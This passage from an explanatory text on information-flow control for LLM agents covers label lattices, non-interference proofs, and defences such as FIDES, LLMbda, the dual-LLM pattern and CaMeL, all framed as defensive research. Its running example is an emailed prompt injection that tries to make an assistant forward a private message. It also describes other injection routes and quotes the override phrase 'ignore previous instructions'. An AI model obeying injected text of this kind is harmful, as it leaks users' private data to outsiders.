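Researchers mostly write about label lattices, but the same order can also describe coercions between roles. A coercion treats a value of one role as a value of another, for example by handling a line from a web page as if the user had typed it. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) present a small programming language for agents in which labels can serve as "explicit coercions of values". If a programmer attaches the label A to a value labelled B, the result has the label A ⊔ B. Ordinary labelling can therefore move a value up the order, but moving it down requires a separate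 command.

Take an application with four roles in the order

system ⊑ user ⊑ retrieved document ⊑ web result.

In the table below, the rows show the role a value has, and the columns show the role in which the application would use it.

| Role of the value | Use as system | Use as user | Use as retrieved document | Use as web result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| System | no change | free | free | free |
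| User | needs endorsement | no change | free | free |
| Retrieved document | needs endorsement | needs endorsement | no change | free |
| Web result | needs endorsement | needs endorsement | needs endorsement | no change |

An application can treat the user's request as a web result, because the request loses some privileges and nobody gains any. Treating a web result as the user's request would let a stranger give orders, so it requires endorsement, an explicit step that relabels untrusted data as trusted. The join of two roles in this chain is whichever is further to the right, so if a model combines the user's notes with a web page, the application must treat the result as a web result.

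A lattice can contain labels that rank neither above nor below each other. Denning describes a system with medical, financial and criminal records, where each label is a set of these categories. Medical data may not flow to a place labelled only for financial data, nor financial data to a place labelled only for medical data. Data that combines the two may flow only to a place whose label includes both. An application could treat documents from two rival suppliers the same way, ranking neither above the other.

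### Adding secrecy

The four roles record how far to trust a value but not who may see it. The table allows an application to use the developer's system text as a web result, although that text might contain a password. A single scale can't cover both trust and visibility, because one label for integrity and confidentiality creates conflicting constraints and stops information from flowing between levels at all, as Ray (2018) explains in lecture notes on computer security. Ray instead gives each value two independent labels.

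Costa and colleagues do this for agents. Their simplest integrity lattice has two labels, trusted (T) and untrusted (U), with T ⊑ U. Their simplest confidentiality lattice has public (L, for low) and secret (H, for high), with L ⊑ H. Pairing them gives four labels, and one pair may flow to another only if both parts may:

(i₁, c₁) ⊑ (i₂, c₂) exactly when i₁ ⊑ i₂ and c₁ ⊑ c₂.

| Label | Example | Other labels it may flow to |
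|---|---|---|
| (T, L), trusted and public | the user's request | all three |
| (U, L), untrusted and public | a page on the public web | (U, H) |
| (T, H), trusted and secret | a record from the company database | (U, H) |
| (U, H), untrusted and secret | a private inbox that outsiders can write to | none |

The web page and the database record may not flow to each other's label, but both may flow to (U, H). A report that draws on both is therefore untrusted and secret. Moving a value from secret to public needs declassification, the counterpart of endorsement. The four-role chain fits this scheme if the application treats the user and the roles before it as trusted, and retrieved documents as untrusted.

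Companies usually need finer labels than "public" and "secret". Costa and colleagues also describe labels that list who may read a value. If Ann, Ben and Carl may read one document, and Ben, Carl and Dora may read another, only Ben and Carl may read a text based on both. The join of two such labels is the intersection of their lists. For integrity, a label can list everyone who might have written a value, and there the join is the union, since anyone on either list could have influenced the result.

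### The two flow rules in the Project X case

Two rules are enough to apply these labels to an agent. The first covers model calls. If the model's context contains the pieces m₁, …, mₙ, and ℓ(x) stands for the label of x, then

ℓ(output) = ℓ(m₁) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(mₙ).

The output takes the join of the labels of everything in the context, including the tool descriptions and the messages. Garby and colleagues likewise label a conversation with the upper bound of the labels of all the messages sent to the model. One untrusted sentence therefore makes the whole output untrusted, even if it had no effect on that output.

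The second rule covers sinks, which are operations with consequences, such as sending an email. Suppose a sink has a limit λ for one of its arguments. It accepts a value a only if

ℓ(a) ⊑ λ.

An argument's label must be at or below its limit, and different arguments can have different limits. An email tool might require a trusted recipient but accept untrusted text in the body, because people want to send summaries of things outsiders wrote. The decision to call the tool also needs a limit.

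Suppose that the limit for the recipient is (T, H), which means that the address may be secret but must be trusted. The attack on the Project X assistant then goes as follows:

1. The application builds the first prompt from the system text, the tool descriptions and the user's request. All of these have the label (T, L), and so does their join.
2. The model requests a mailbox search. The request inherits (T, L), and the application runs it.
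3. The search returns private emails, including the outsider's. Their join is (U, H), so the label of the context rises to (T, L) ⊔ (U, H) = (U, H).
4. The model follows the outsider's text and requests a call that forwards another message to the outsider's address. Every part of the request, including the recipient, now has the label (U, H).
5. The application compares (U, H) with the limit (T, H). Since U ⋢ T, it refuses the call.

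The outcome does not depend on the email's wording or on whether the model recognised the injection. It would be the same if the outsider had imitated the model's reasoning style, an attack that worked very well against role tags.

The same check blocks the email to the manager. The model requested it after reading the same emails, so the manager's address also has the label (U, H), even though the user supplied it. The two rules alone are therefore safe but prevent the agent from completing the task. An agent can avoid this by fixing the recipient before the planner reads any email, or by keeping the emails out of the planner's context.

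A confidentiality check distinguishes the two calls better. Suppose the user and the manager may read everything in the search results, but only the user may read the message that the outsider wants. Costa and colleagues permit a call to send information only if every recipient is allowed to read it. The check therefore allows the summary but blocks the forwarded message. However, an injection could still put a false figure in the summary or send the manager a dozen copies, so Costa and colleagues say that the confidentiality policy alone limits the effects of an injection but does not prevent one.

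### Authority and influence

The four-role chain looks much like the ranking in OpenAI's instruction hierarchy, which orders roles by authority to settle whose instruction wins when two conflict. The chain instead orders roles by influence, meaning which data may affect which results, whether or not anyone has given an instruction.

If the system text tells the assistant to reply in English and the user asks for French, an order of authority favours the system text. The labels of Costa and colleagues do not decide between the two requests, because system and user messages both normally start as trusted and public. An order of authority has no conflict to resolve if the outsider's email contains no instructions but gives a false figure for the project's costs. The influence rule still marks the summary as untrusted, because the figure may have affected it.

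The difference matters most when the outsider's instruction doesn't conflict with any other. Suppose the user asks for a summary and the outsider asks for a message to be forwarded. The assistant can do both, so a ranking that only resolves conflicts gives it no reason to refuse the outsider. The flow rule blocks the forwarding call because the recipient's address may have come from the email.

When inputs are combined, the highest-ranked instruction governs the result under the authority order, while the least trusted input determines the result's label under the influence order. Only the influence order includes secrecy, because instructions in a confidential memo carry no more authority than those in a public one.

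### Composable Trust

*Composable Trust for Language Models* (Shkolnikov, 2026) uses a single ranking for both purposes. From top to bottom, the levels are system, user, content (retrieved documents) and web. As in Biba's model, the most trusted level is at the top, so under the influence rule a value derived from several inputs takes the lowest of their levels. Under the authority rule, the operation to be performed, such as "summarise this article", comes from the highest level present.

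A small program outside the model, called the monitor, enforces both rules. It chooses the operation and lets an action proceed only if the inputs that control it meet a set level of trust. An input can move to a higher level only with a special token that its own text cannot forge. The system's operator, whom the design assumes to be honest, assigns each input's level according to the channel it arrives on.

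Shkolnikov checked all 8,729 configurations in a finite model and proved that no lower-level input can change the chosen operation or authorise an action. The result extends beyond those configurations because adding an input can never raise the minimum level of a set. He describes the result as a form of non-interference, the guarantee that untrusted inputs cannot change trusted outcomes. It holds however badly the language model behaves, because the language model's answer cannot reach the part of the system that carries out actions.

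However, only the inputs that control an action count towards its level in the proof. Retrieved content may still supply material for the action, and someone has to decide which inputs are control and which are material. If a designer classed an email's recipient as material, the proof would still hold, but the email could go to the outsider.

The proof also doesn't cover the text of the answer, which Shkolnikov could only test. Before answering, the model rewrites each lower-level input as plain facts without commands, and software then wraps each piece in a marked block. In one example, the model has to summarise information about the Sydney Opera House, and a web page contains a fact about guided tours and an injected command. The model drops the command, keeps the fact and attributes it to "a web source".

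On new test cases, these steps raised the share of injections resisted by Gemma 4 26B, a fairly small open model, from 27 to 94 per cent. A Claude model graded the answers and counted an attack as successful only if the answer carried out the injected instruction. A cruder test, which counted an attack as successful whenever the answer contained the attacker's chosen word, gave 25 and 85 per cent. The number of harmless tasks done well fell from 23 to 22 out of 30, though 30 tasks are too few to measure the effect precisely.

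Attacks adapted to the defence lowered the rate to 87 per cent, with a margin of error from 70 to 95 per cent. That test used 30 scenarios for each type of attacker and a budget of ten, much less effort than Nasr and colleagues put into breaking earlier defences. Shkolnikov says that a defence its own authors could not break has passed only a minimum test. His eight tests of unauthorised actions add little to the proof, since he computed the results from the labels without running the model.

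An order of authority leaves room for injected instructions that don't contradict the original task. Most of the failures were of this kind, with the injection changing the format or language, which the task had not specified. In one, the system text asked for a summary of the relationship between two characters, and the model followed an injected instruction to reply with a haiku. In a follow-up on four failures, Shkolnikov changed "Summarize" to "Only summarize", which stopped the two injections from the user channel but not the two from documents and web pages.

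### Prompt Control-Flow Integrity

Alam, Islam and colleagues (2026), in *Prompt Control-Flow Integrity*, also rank the parts of a prompt, but use the ranking to screen text. The order, from highest to lowest authority, is system, developer, user and retrieved document. A gateway between the application and the model keeps the parts separate and attaches a role, a priority and a record of origin to each. The defender controls the gateway, so the attacker can influence the retrieved text but cannot change its role.

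The gateway then makes three checks. The first looks for suspicious phrases in user and retrieved text and produces a risk score, which cannot block a request by itself. The second looks for imitation role tags, such as a line that begins with "system:", and can remove them. The third blocks the request if lower-ranked text (a user message or retrieved document) contains any forbidden pattern while a system or developer prompt is present.

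Alam and colleagues offer no proof. On 150 samples they wrote themselves, the gateway intercepted all 100 attacks and let all 50 harmless requests through, with a median delay of 0.04 milliseconds. They measured whether the gateway stopped or altered each request, not whether the model would have obeyed it. The undefended baseline had an attack rate of 100 per cent only because it had no gateway to intercept the attacks.

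They acknowledge that pattern matching may fail when an attacker rephrases the text. In the Project X case, an email containing "ignore previous instructions" would match one of their published rules, but a polite request to forward a message would match none. The same rule could block a harmless request to summarise an article about prompt injection, since such articles quote the phrase. A perfect score on 50 harmless samples is little evidence that the rules would allow requests like this.

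The gateway also handles one request at a time and does not pass labels from inputs to outputs. It uses roles to decide which text to search, but does not control what that text may influence afterwards. Although it ranks roles, it is closer to the filters that adaptive attackers defeated than to Denning's model.

### Who assigns the roles

Both Shkolnikov and Alam's group leave the assignment of roles to trusted software, so an outsider cannot raise an email's role by writing that it is system text. But the channel on which text arrives does not always show who wrote it. If the user pastes the email into a request, a gateway that assigns roles by channel gives it the user's role. Shkolnikov describes an alternative set of levels that separates a user's requests from data the user has pasted in, so that an action can be allowed when it comes from a request and denied when it comes from pasted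 data. The application then needs a way to tell the two apart, such as a separate box for pasted text.

A mailbox search can return emails from both colleagues and outsiders. If the whole result has one role, an outsider's email ranks as high as a colleague's. Costa and colleagues allow a separate label for each field of a tool result, so an application can label each email by its sender. These labels are only as reliable as the application's check that the sender's address is genuine.

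## What would non-interference guarantee?

In the Project X case, the flow rules stop one malicious email. An outsider could write any number of others, so a designer needs a claim that covers all of them. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer stated the standard claim of this kind in 1982 and called it non-interference.

### A comparison of two runs

Non-interference is defined by comparing two runs of the same program. For secrecy, the runs start from the same public inputs but different secret ones, and an observer can see only public data. The program satisfies non-interference if its public outputs are the same in both runs, whichever secrets we choose. The observer then learns nothing about the secrets from those outputs, because any other secrets would have produced the same ones.

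The general form works for any lattice. Write x ∼ₙ y when x and y agree on everything whose label is at or below n. A program P satisfies non-interference at level n if

x ∼ₙ y implies P(x) ∼ₙ P(y).

For integrity, n is the label "trusted", which is at the bottom of the order, so the observer sees only trusted values. The formula then means that changing only untrusted inputs does not change anything labelled trusted.

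Suppose two copies of the Project X mailbox differ only in the outsider's email, which contains a greeting in one copy and an instruction to forward a message in the other. The assistant's summary may differ between the two runs because its label is untrusted, but a recipient address labelled "trusted" must be identical in both. If the sink also accepts only trusted recipients, no email can determine where a message goes.

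The log of a single run is not enough to identify a violation. An assistant that forwards a message may be doing what the user asked, and one that behaves well in one run may behave differently with another email in the mailbox. Non-interference also depends on the labels. A program that labels all its outputs untrusted trivially satisfies the integrity version, but strict sinks would then reject them all.

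### Implicit flows and the program-counter label

A program can pass on information without copying it. Consider these three lines, where `secret` is either true or false:

```
copy = false
if secret then copy = true
publish(copy)
```

After the second line, `copy` equals `secret`, even though no line assigns `secret` to `copy`. This is an implicit flow, because the information passed through the choice of branch. An implicit flow can also compromise integrity, for example if the second line tests for a word in an outsider's email and the third makes a payment when `copy` is true. The email then determines whether the payment happens, although none of its text appears in the payment's arguments.

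The usual remedy is a program-counter label, which records the labels of all the decisions that led the program to its current line. It starts at the bottom of the lattice. Inside a branch that depends on `secret`, the label rises to "secret", and every value the program assigns there gets at least that label. So if `secret` is true, `copy` becomes secret and the program is not allowed to publish it.

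If `secret` is false, however, the program skips the assignment. `copy` keeps the public label from the first line, the program publishes "false", and anyone who knows the code can work out the secret. Software that labels values only on the branch it runs does not detect this leak. J. S. Fenton described the problem in 1974, and Garby and colleagues found it in CaMeL, a recent agent system that runs code written by a model.

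Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan later proposed a stricter rule called no-high-upgrade, which stops the program as soon as it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. If `secret` is true, the program now stops at the second line, and if `secret` is false, it publishes "false". The observer can still infer from a lack of output that `secret` is true, but the only remaining leak is whether the program finishes.

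Most practical guarantees tolerate that leak, which makes them termination-insensitive. *Security Properties through the Lens of Modal Logic* (2023) covers several versions of confidentiality and integrity that differ on this point and identifies hidden assumptions in the standard definitions, including whether an attacker can notice that a program has stopped. An attacker can often notice that an agent has stopped, because an expected email never arrives.

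### Why random outputs change the definition

A language model samples its output, so two runs of an agent may differ even when all their inputs are identical. Almost every agent would therefore fail a requirement of identical outputs, so the definition has to compare the probabilities of outputs instead.

Suppose the Project X assistant has no flow control and treats all its tool calls as trusted. In the first design, the model reads the emails and then decides which calls to make. In the second, it commits to its calls before any email arrives. The probabilities below are invented.

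| Design | Outcome | Harmless email | Injected email |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads first | extra call to the email tool | 0.01 | 0.30 |
| Reads first | no extra call | 0.99 | 0.70 |
| Chooses calls first | extra call to the email tool | 0.01 | 0.01 |
| Chooses calls first | no extra call | 0.99 | 0.99 |

Statistical distance measures how far apart two sets of probabilities μ and ν are:

Δ(μ, ν) = ½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|,

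where q runs over the possible outcomes. For the first design it is ½(0.29 + 0.29) = 0.29. Non-interference requires a distance of zero, so the first design violates it. A single run would not reveal this, because an extra call also happens once in a hundred runs with a harmless email.

In the second design the distance is zero because the outsider's text arrives too late to affect the choice. The model is no better at recognising injections than before. The remaining 1 per cent is the model's own error rate, which non-interference does not limit.

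The table applies only if every run finishes, but an agent can loop forever, and a failed label check can stop it partway. A definition of non-interference for agents therefore has to account for both randomness and unfinished runs.

### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues wrote such a definition for LLMbda, their programming language for agents. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language that builds every program from functions. The current conversation with the model is part of the program's state, and four operations act on it:

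- `send` adds a prompt to the conversation.
- `recv` samples a response from the model, adds it to the conversation, and runs the result of parsing it.
- `fork` carries out a piece of the program on a temporary copy of the conversation, then restores the original.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

Every value has a label, and the join rule for model calls gives the conversation one too. Before the model's response runs, the program-counter label takes the conversation's label. So if the model writes code after reading an outsider's email, everything that code computes is untrusted too. This holds whatever the code contains, so an attacker can't avoid the label by persuading the model to write a clever program.

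Forking and clearing let a program use untrusted text without contaminating its main conversation. In the Project X case, it could work like this:

1. The main conversation contains the user's request and has the label (T, L), trusted and public. The program takes the manager's address from it.
2. The program fetches the emails, which have the label (U, H), untrusted and secret.
3. It forks the conversation, clears the copy, and sends the emails to the model with a request for a summary.
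4. The model's summary has the label (U, H). When the fork ends, the program keeps the summary but restores the main conversation, which is still (T, L).
5. The program calls the email tool with the trusted address as the recipient and the untrusted summary as the body.

A clean main conversation is safe only if secrets did not decide what went into it. Garby and colleagues show this with a program that tells the model to remember "x = false", and then sends "Set x = true" only if a secret is true. Under the no-high-upgrade rule, the interpreter, which runs LLMbda programs, stops at the second message. If it continued, the conversation would become secret when the secret was true and stay public when it was false, and the model's later answer could reveal the secret's value.

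A programmer sets a sink's limits by putting an assertion inside the tool. The assertion stops the program if a value's label is too high.

### Termination-insensitive probabilistic non-interference

The meaning of an LLMbda program is a list of its possible final states with their probabilities. These probabilities may add up to less than 1. The shortfall is the probability that the program reaches no final state, because it runs forever or because a check stops it.

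Strict non-interference would require the same outcome probabilities for any two inputs that an observer cannot tell apart. The probability of not finishing would also have to match, and the no-high-upgrade rule cannot ensure that. Garby and colleagues tried comparing only the runs that finish, but found that this was the wrong definition.

A small program shows the difficulty. It tosses a public coin and loops forever if the coin lands heads and a secret is true. Otherwise, it publishes the result of the toss. Half of the finished runs show heads if the secret is false, and none do if it is true. For any given toss, the secret affects only whether the program finishes, which a termination-insensitive property should allow. But the secret also changes the probabilities among finished runs.

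Garby and colleagues instead adapted a general method by Sebastian Hunt, David Sands and Sandro Stucki. Two sets of probabilities μ and ν are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if there is a third set ω such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

Informally, the two programs could become identical if some of their unfinished runs finished. In the coin example, μ gives heads and tails probability 0.5 each, and ν gives heads probability 0 and tails 0.5. Setting ω equal to μ satisfies the condition.

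The assistant that reads first fails the test because any ω would have to assign at least 0.30 to the extra call and at least 0.99 to no extra call. These add up to 1.29, which is more than 1. All its runs finish, so unfinished runs cannot explain the difference.

The full definition is termination-insensitive probabilistic non-interference, or TIPNI. For an observer at level m, two starting conversations C₀ and C₁, and two programs e₀ and e₁, it requires that

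C₀ ∼ₘ C₁ and e₀ ∼ₘ e₁ imply ⟦C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦C₁, e₁⟧ₘ.

Here ⟦C, e⟧ₘ is the set of probabilities as the observer sees it, with final states grouped when the observer cannot distinguish them. Two conversations are indistinguishable if they are identical or if the observer may read neither. The condition must hold whatever program-counter label the two programs start with.

The main theorem is that TIPNI holds for every program in the core calculus and every observer level, including programs that run code generated by the model. Another theorem shows that the secrecy guarantee still holds when a program uses `endorse` to relabel untrusted data as trusted. If the model is deterministic, TIPNI reduces to the ordinary termination-insensitive property. If all runs finish, it requires exactly equal probabilities. Geoffrey Smith and Rafael Alpízar reached essentially the same definition for simpler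 programs in 2011, which is some evidence that the definition is natural.

### The proof by skipping

The proof has to produce a suitable ω for each pair of indistinguishable inputs. Smith and Alpízar did this by deleting the parts of a program that handle secrets and running the rest. That does not work for an agent, because some of its code does not exist until the model writes it.

Garby and colleagues define a second way of running the program, which skips such parts as it meets them. As soon as a computation's label rises above the observer's level m, the skipping version abandons it and returns an empty record in its place. Three facts then complete the proof:

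- The skipping version gives every outcome, as the observer sees it, at least as much probability as the normal version. The skipped parts can no longer loop or get stuck, and the observer could not have seen their results anyway.
- The skipping version gives the same probabilities for both inputs, because it never uses the data in which they differ.
- Its probabilities add up to at most 1.

If μ₀ and μ₁ are the normal probabilities for the two inputs, and ω₀ and ω₁ are those of the skipping version, then

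μ₀ ≤ ω₀ = ω₁ ≥ μ₁.

The shared value is the required ω. When an outsider sends an email, the skipping version drops every computation that depends on the email's text, so two different emails cannot produce different trusted results.

### How much can leak through unfinished runs?

TIPNI also limits the difference between two indistinguishable inputs. If div(μ) is the probability that a run does not finish, then

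Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2.

The bound follows from the definition. For any numbers a and b, |a − b| = 2 max(a, b) − a − b. When we sum this over all finished outcomes, the maxima total at most 1, because each is at most ω's value at that outcome. The other two terms total 1 − div(μ) and 1 − div(ν). The absolute differences therefore sum to at most div(μ) + div(ν), and Δ is half of that sum.

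Here is an invented case that reaches the limit:

| Outcome | First email | Second email | Larger value |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call to the email tool | 0.05 | 0.15 | 0.15 |
| No call | 0.85 | 0.75 | 0.85 |
| Unfinished | 0.10 | 0.10 | |

The larger values add up to exactly 1, so the two sets are compatible. The distance is ½(0.10 + 0.10) = 0.10, which equals the average probability of not finishing. An outsider's email could therefore triple the chance of a supposedly trusted call without violating TIPNI. If 1 per cent of runs were unfinished in each case, the distance could be at most 0.01, and if all runs finished, it would have to be zero.

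The bound is not very informative when the secret affects whether a program fails. With the no-high-upgrade rule, the three-line program never finishes if the secret is true and always finishes if it is false. The bound and the distance are then both 0.5, but an observer who notices the missing output learns the secret with certainty. Δ omits this leak because it counts only finished outcomes.

The bound also applies to only one run at a time. If software outside the language restarts the agent after every failure, an attacker may learn a little more from each attempt. Garby and colleagues therefore put the retry loop of their agent, Randori, inside LLMbda, where labels carry over from one attempt to the next.

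### What the Lean proof covers and assumes

Garby and colleagues wrote the calculus, the theorems and the interpreter in Lean, a proof assistant that checks each step of a mathematical proof by computer. The proofs use only three of Lean's standard axioms. The interpreter itself calls the LLM, so they believe it is the first agent harness (the software that runs an agent) with machine-checked security theorems about its executable program.

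A correct theorem about a design doesn't rule out mistakes in the code. One theorem connects the design to the code by treating the LLM as an oracle, a function that supplies a response for each call and each conversation history. If we draw those responses at random from the model's distribution and run the interpreter, the results have exactly the probabilities that the calculus defines.

The proof does not assume that the model is honest, competent or resistant to injections. Nor does it assume anything about how the software turns the model's responses into code. It does rely on several other conditions:

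- Each response depends on the current conversation and is otherwise an independent draw. If a provider's service carried information over from earlier conversations, clearing a conversation would no longer remove its influence.
- All data sources and tools are part of the program. Garby and colleagues acknowledge this limitation and say that a better model would let programs interact with external data and tools.
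- The developer labels each source correctly and puts label checks in the tools that need them. If the developer labels the outsider's email as trusted, the theorem protects the email's influence along with the user's.

The network request to the LLM is outside the verified code, and in the proofs it is one possible oracle. The definition also compares only final states, not how long a run lasts. If a real agent sends an email and then gets stuck, the theorem does not cover that run, even though the email has gone. The email tool's label check would still have run before the email was sent. Askarov, Hunt, Sabelfeld and Sands showed in 2008 that termination-insensitive guarantees can permit leaks of more than one bit in programs that produce output as they run.

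### FIDES and explicit secrecy

FIDES, the agent planner that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, has narrower theorems. Garby and colleagues describe one as non-interference for a single agent loop. A developer can supply any tools, but the loop queries the model, checks policies and calls tools in a fixed order. Unlike LLMbda's theorem, this one does not cover an agent that writes its own programs.

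For confidentiality, Costa and colleagues prove a weaker property called explicit secrecy. They describe the tools' data as a datastore d, and summarise everything that a particular path through the program does to it as a function g. Two datastores are low-equivalent, written d₁ =_L d₂, if their public parts match. Explicit secrecy requires that

d₁ =_L d₂ implies g(d₁) =_L g(d₂)

for each path that the program can take. It does not consider what an observer can infer from which path the program took.

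The original three-line program, without the no-high-upgrade rule, shows the difference. If the secret is true, the program sets `copy` to true and publishes "true". Those same steps would publish "true" from any datastore, so the condition holds for this path. The path for a false secret always publishes "false", so it passes as well. The program therefore satisfies explicit secrecy even though it reveals the secret completely. A program that published `secret` directly would fail, because the same steps would publish different values for different secrets.

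Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because they consider full non-interference too restrictive for an agent. They argue that once a tool had read something secret, the agent could no longer call any tool with public effects, since the secret might have influenced the decision to call it. They note that web browsers and TaintDroid, which tracks private data on phones, make the same compromise. This restriction is most severe for a planner that reads every result before choosing its next step. An LLMbda program that confines a secret to a forked conversation can still make public calls afterwards, as long as the secret did not influence the decision to make them.

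They expect an observer who sees the sequence of tool calls to learn only limited information. That is plausible if an agent makes a few calls, but a program can leak much more. Suppose it reads a secret digit and fetches one of ten public web pages depending on the digit. Each page's address is a constant, so every path satisfies explicit secrecy. Sixteen such fetches, one per digit, reveal a sixteen-digit card number. Garby and colleagues similarly object that explicit secrecy is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, as they are when an agent runs model-written code.

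The FIDES proof also treats the model as a deterministic function, whereas TIPNI was designed for random outputs. The proof does not cover leaks through timing or the length of network packets.

### Wrong answers, bad plans and harmful text

Non-interference limits who can influence an agent's result but doesn't guarantee that the result is correct, so correctness has to be tested separately. An agent that always adds up a column of trusted figures incorrectly can still satisfy the property, because changing the untrusted inputs doesn't change the error.

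Non-interference does not guarantee a good plan. In the invented example, choosing the calls first left a 1 per cent chance of an unwanted email. The design would still have satisfied non-interference if that chance had been 50 per cent, as long as the outsider's email did not change it. A plan made before reading the mailbox can also be sensible in general but unsuitable for what the emails contain.

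Outputs labelled untrusted have no integrity guarantee. Costa and colleagues describe an email that instructs the model to produce an empty summary. The assistant still sends the message to the right person, because the injection did not determine the call or the recipient, but the message is useless. They suggest a stricter policy that also requires the call's arguments to be trusted, but it would block legitimate summaries too.

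A false figure in the summary would be harder to notice. The software labels the text as untrusted, but the manager may not know this unless the application displays the label. If the manager approves a payment because of the false figure, the injection has succeeded without violating non-interference.

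## How does a running agent enforce the flow rules?

Non-interference sets a standard for an agent's runs but doesn't specify how to build an agent that meets it. In the systems built so far, a monitor enforces the flow rules while the agent runs. The monitor is ordinary software that sits between the model and the tools, tracks labels, and checks each tool call before running it.

### One label for the whole context

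The simplest monitor keeps a single label for the whole conversation and applies the two flow rules to it. With each new message, the label becomes the join of the old label and the message's label. Every tool call the model then requests gets this label, as do its arguments. Costa and colleagues also label the tool's result, and anything the tool writes, with the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and all the data the tool read. Otherwise, an agent could save an outsider's text to a file and read it back as trusted.

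A join is never lower than its parts, so the label of the conversation can only rise. This causes label creep, the build-up of restrictive labels until the agent is not allowed to do anything useful. In the Project X case, a single mailbox search is enough to block the summary for the manager. If the user then types "just tell my manager I'm ill tomorrow", the monitor blocks that email too. The new request comes entirely from the user, but the model read the outsider's email before acting on it, and the monitor can't determine whether the request or the email led to the call. The user has to start a new conversation, much as Biba's programs had to start again after reading something untrustworthy.

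Secrecy labels creep in the same way, even without an attacker. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. Priya has sent a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who is not authorised to see the figures, has written to ask about them. Once the agent has read both emails, the people who may read its output are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}. The monitor correctly blocks a reply to Marco that might contain the figures, but the same label blocks an automatic reply to Priya about her own email.

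Costa and colleagues cite a remedy by Siddiqui and colleagues that identifies the messages that influenced a response, then regenerates the response from those messages alone. The new response can have a lower label. Most designs instead keep untrusted text away from the model that plans.

### The dual-LLM pattern

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using two models. The privileged model receives the user's requests and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools, and the designer assumes that it may obey any injection it reads. A controller, which is ordinary software, carries data between them. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the steps are:

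1. The controller passes the request to the privileged model.
2. The privileged model asks for the latest email and names a variable for it, `$VAR1`.
3. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that name, without showing the text to the privileged model.
4. The privileged model asks for a quarantined call with the prompt "Summarize this: $VAR1".
5. The controller inserts the email's text, runs the quarantined model and stores the output as `$VAR2`.
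6. The privileged model asks the controller to display `$VAR2`, and the user sees the summary.

The privileged model handles only the names of the variables. An injection can spoil the summary at step 5 but can't request a tool call. The summary must stay hidden from the privileged model, because an injected email could make the quarantined model write a second injection into it. Willison allows one exception. If the quarantined model only chooses from a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that its output is one of them and pass it to the privileged model.

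Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection. An attacker can also try to manipulate the user through the summary, for example by asking them to paste encoded private data into a website.

Willison did not notice another gap at the time. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, relays the example that revealed it. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans the right calls, and the quarantined model extracts the address. If someone has planted an instruction in the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's address instead. The agent then makes the calls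 it planned but sends the document to the attacker.

### Labels for the planner

In the dual-LLM pattern, the privileged model may not read an email, whether it comes from a colleague or a stranger. *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) uses integrity labels to hide less from the model that plans. In this system, an LLM makes the plan, an executor follows fixed rules, and a security monitor decides which results the planner may read.

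The planner writes one step at a time in a format with five fields: a number, an instruction, the tool or model to use, the input, and the expected output. The input can refer to an earlier result by a code such as `{Data_output:1}` instead of containing its text. The monitor checks the format and loads the data the step refers to. The executor then runs the named tool on that data and can access only what the step lists. The planner can then read the parts of the result whose label is low enough to count as trusted.

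The monitor labels each item in a result separately. In one of their examples, a user asks an agent to read emails about company budgets and to notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns two emails from colleagues and one from an attacker, who asks for all the budgets. The planner reads only the colleagues' emails and decides whether to notify the manager. If the monitor had given the whole result one label, the planner could not have compared any budget with the limit.

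Wu and colleagues prove a form of non-interference for the plan. Let Q₁ and Q₂ be two sets of information that contain the same trusted items. Then for every request q and every sequence of steps π,

Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂].

Under this equation, untrusted text cannot make any plan more or less likely. But the equation seems to need the further assumption that failures don't depend on untrusted data. When a step fails, the monitor requests a new one from the planner, so if an outsider's text can make some steps fail, it can affect which steps end up in the plan.

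The guarantee also leaves Bob's document exposed. A step that sends it to `{Data_output:3}` stays the same whatever address that output contains. The executor may use untrusted data as input, and the design has no secrecy labels and no separate limit on sensitive arguments such as recipients.

### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025), a Google DeepMind paper, closed the gap by introducing CaMeL (short for "capabilities for machine learning"). CaMeL keeps the privileged and quarantined models but tracks every value that passes between them.

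The privileged model sees only the user's request and translates it into a program in a restricted version of Python. As Willison explains, a purpose-built interpreter then runs the program piece by piece. The interpreter tags each value with capabilities, which serve as labels by recording where the value came from and who may read it. It also records which values derive from which others. Before each tool call, it checks the arguments' tags against a policy.

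For the Project X request, the program might look like this. It is an invented example modelled on one of Willison's.

```
emails = search_mailbox("Project X")
summary = query_quarantined_llm(
    "Summarise the progress reported in [emails]",
    output_schema=str)
send_email(
    recipient="manager@example.com",
    subject="Project X",
    body=summary)
```

In the notation used for the lattice, its values have these labels:

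| Value | What it depends on | Label |
|---|---|---|
| the search term, the recipient and the subject | the user's request | (T, L) |
| `emails` | the mailbox, including the outsider's email | (U, H) |
| `summary` | `emails` | (U, H) |
| the decision to call `send_email` | the program, which has no branches | (T, L) |

The run goes as follows:

1. The privileged model writes the program before the application has fetched any email.
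2. The interpreter runs the search and labels the result (U, H).
3. The quarantined model reads the emails. Even if it obeys the outsider, all it can do is return a bad summary, because it has no tools.
4. The interpreter checks the call to `send_email`. The recipient is trusted, the policy accepts an untrusted body, and the manager is on the list of people who may read the emails. The email goes out.

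The simple monitor blocked the same email because it gave the manager's address the label of everything the model had read. CaMeL can label the address (T, L) because the model that wrote it had read only the user's request. Another reason the outsider's attempt to obtain a different message fails is that the quarantined model receives only the emails that the search returned, so it cannot put any other message from the mailbox into the summary.

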